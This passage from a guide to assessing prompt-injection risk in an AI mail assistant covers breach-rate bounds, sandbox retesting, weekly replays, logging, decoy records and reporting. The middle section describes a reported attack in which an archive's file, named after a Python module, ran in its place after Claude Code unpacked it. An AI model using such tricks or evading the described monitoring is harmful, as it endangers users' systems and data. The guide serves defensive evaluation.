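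The company could stop the model from writing replies and use it only to sort messages into fixed categories, with a reviewed program handling each category. For a delivery question, ordinary code would find the customer from the sender's address and copy the order's status and delivery date into a standard reply. Without `search_files` and `send_reply`, the model could leak another customer's record only through a fault in the code or an error in the company's records.

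Testers can now assume that the attacker controls the model completely, as Willison recommends whenever hostile text reaches a model. They then only need to test the code, which is fast because no model has to run. Suppose they send it 30,000 varied requests for the wrong customer's record or a reply to the wrong address, and the code blocks them all. The upper bound on the breach rate is then 0.01%. That means at most 0.1 breaches a year and at most a 9.5% chance of one or more, which is within the company's 10% limit.

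That calculation treats a hole in the code as a random failure, but an attacker who finds one will use it every time. Littlewood and Strigini suggest using evidence from reviews and proofs to support the claim that software has no faults, rather than a claim that it has a particular failure rate. If a careful review justifies 95% confidence that the code has no hole, the chance of a leak through the code is at most 5%, no matter how many hostile messages arrive. A small lookup program is much easier to review this way than a language model. Strigini (2025) notes that writing out the argument for an outlandish claim often leads to a more modest one that evidence can support.

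### What voids an estimate

Christodorescu and colleagues stress that a security assessment applies only to the components, request types and policy that the assessors examined. If any of these changes, the system needs a new assessment. The terms of the breach formula show which tests to repeat.

| Change | What it can alter | What to do |
|---|---|---|
| New model version | h, and e if the model can look for holes in the sandbox | Repeat the adaptive attack test and the escape tests |
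| New system prompt or tool description | h | Repeat the adaptive attack test |
| New tool or wider permission | s, and the routes that e has to cover | Replay old hijacks against the policy, then attack the complete system |
| Update to the gateway, proxy or container | e | Repeat the forbidden requests |
| New attack technique | Any of the three | Add the technique to the attack test and run it |
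| More hostile messages, or more sensitive data | The acceptable rate | Recalculate the limit |

An estimate that already assumes every exposure leads to a hijack stays valid after some of these changes. In the redesigned mail assistant, a new model can only choose from the same categories, so the company doesn't have to repeat the leak test when it changes models. It should still check how often the new model chooses correctly.

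New attacks are the hardest change to notice because nothing in the company's own system has changed. In August 2026 Willison discussed a test in which Trajectory Labs ran 720 attacks over 72 scenarios against Claude Code's auto mode, and none succeeded. Less than three weeks later, he described an attack by the security researcher Johann Rehberger that reportedly worked 80% of the time. It led Claude Code to unpack an archive and run a program that imported a standard Python module. The archive contained a file with the same name as another module the program needed, so Python ran the attacker's file instead.

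In some runs Claude noticed the malicious program and tried to stop it, but auto mode blocked the command. A reader pointed out to Willison that this wasn't really prompt injection, since the model never followed a hostile instruction. The 720 failures remain good evidence about those 72 scenarios, but they are weak evidence about a different kind of attack.

An outside provider may also update a model when the company has changed nothing, which Patil and colleagues list as a reason that ordinary software tests no longer suffice. The company should lock the model version in its settings if the provider allows it. It can also replay the same 500 hostile messages every week. If these normally produce about 10 hijacks, 20 or more would occur by chance in only about 0.3% of weeks, so that result would justify a full test. Replays can detect changes in the model but not changes in attackers' methods,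 so the company also needs new adaptive tests on a fixed schedule, and an extra one whenever someone publishes a technique that could work on its system.

### Decoys, logs and incident counts

David C recommends logging enough to recognise suspicious activity, perhaps including everything the model reads and writes as well as its tool calls. Attackers usually have to refine an attack, so failed calls may reveal one early. With the narrower permissions and the invented rates, 1,000 hostile messages a year would cause about 20 hijacks. Nearly all of them would lead to a refused call, and a breach would happen about once every two and a half years, so the company would have many chances to notice an attack before one succeeded.

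However, an attacker who knows the policy can avoid forbidden calls and leave nothing unusual in that part of the log. Honest requests that the policy didn't anticipate can also lead to refused calls, so someone has to read the refused calls.

Decoy data can expose leaks that use only permitted calls. The company could add invented customers to its database, each with a unique reference number, and have the mail server raise an alarm if one of those numbers appears in an outgoing message. No legitimate reply would contain one, so false alarms should be very rare. Suppose ten of 1,000 records are decoys. An attacker who steals 100 records at random has a 65% chance of taking at least one decoy, but one who steals a single record has a 1% chance. An attacker who requests only a specific real customer's record will never take a decoy. The alarm also fails if the model rewrites the number or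 leaves it out.

A year with no known breaches is weaker evidence of security than it seems. Rehberger, whom Willison quotes, warns that organisations "confuse the absence of a successful attack with the presence of robust security". Suppose the company keeps the starting permissions, which lead to an average of four breaches a year. If it notices a quarter of breaches and they are independent, it has a 37% chance of noticing none that year. To turn the count into a breach rate, it also needs to know how many hostile messages arrived, and it may not recognise the ones that failed.

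Known breaches are more informative. If the narrower permissions had a breach rate of 0.042%, one breach in a year would be unremarkable, but two or more would happen in only about 7% of years. The company could decide to investigate and repair the cause of any breach, and to withdraw the permission after a second. It should set this rule before the first breach, when nobody yet has a reason to explain one away.

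### Reporting the result

Littlewood and Strigini want every reliability claim to include the level of confidence the evidence supports. A short report on a sandbox also has to name the attacker and the conditions that would invalidate the result. The example describes the redesigned mail assistant and uses invented results.

| Item | Example |
|---|---|
| System | Mail assistant 3.0, with the exact versions of the model, prompt, tools, policy and code |
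| Harmful effect | One customer's delivery details reach another outsider |
| Attacker | Knows the policy and code, and controls everything the model writes |
| Test | 30,000 varied forbidden requests, sent directly to the code in December 2026 |
| Result | No successes; 95% upper bound of 0.01% per request |
| Legitimate work | Answered 470 of 500 delivery questions correctly; sent the other 30 to an employee |
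| Expected use | 1,000 exposures a year; at the upper bound, a 9.5% chance of at least one breach |
| Limit | 10% a year |
| Assumptions | Customer addresses are correct, data has no other way out, and the requests resemble an attacker's |
| Retest | After any change to the tools, policy or code, after a relevant new attack, and by June 2027 |

If the result depends on the model resisting attacks, the report also needs the number of scenarios, techniques and attempts per scenario, and whether the attacker revised its messages after each failure. For a shorter summary, the company could write: "None of 30,000 forbidden requests succeeded, so the failure rate for requests like these is below 0.01% with 95% confidence, even if an attacker controls the model."
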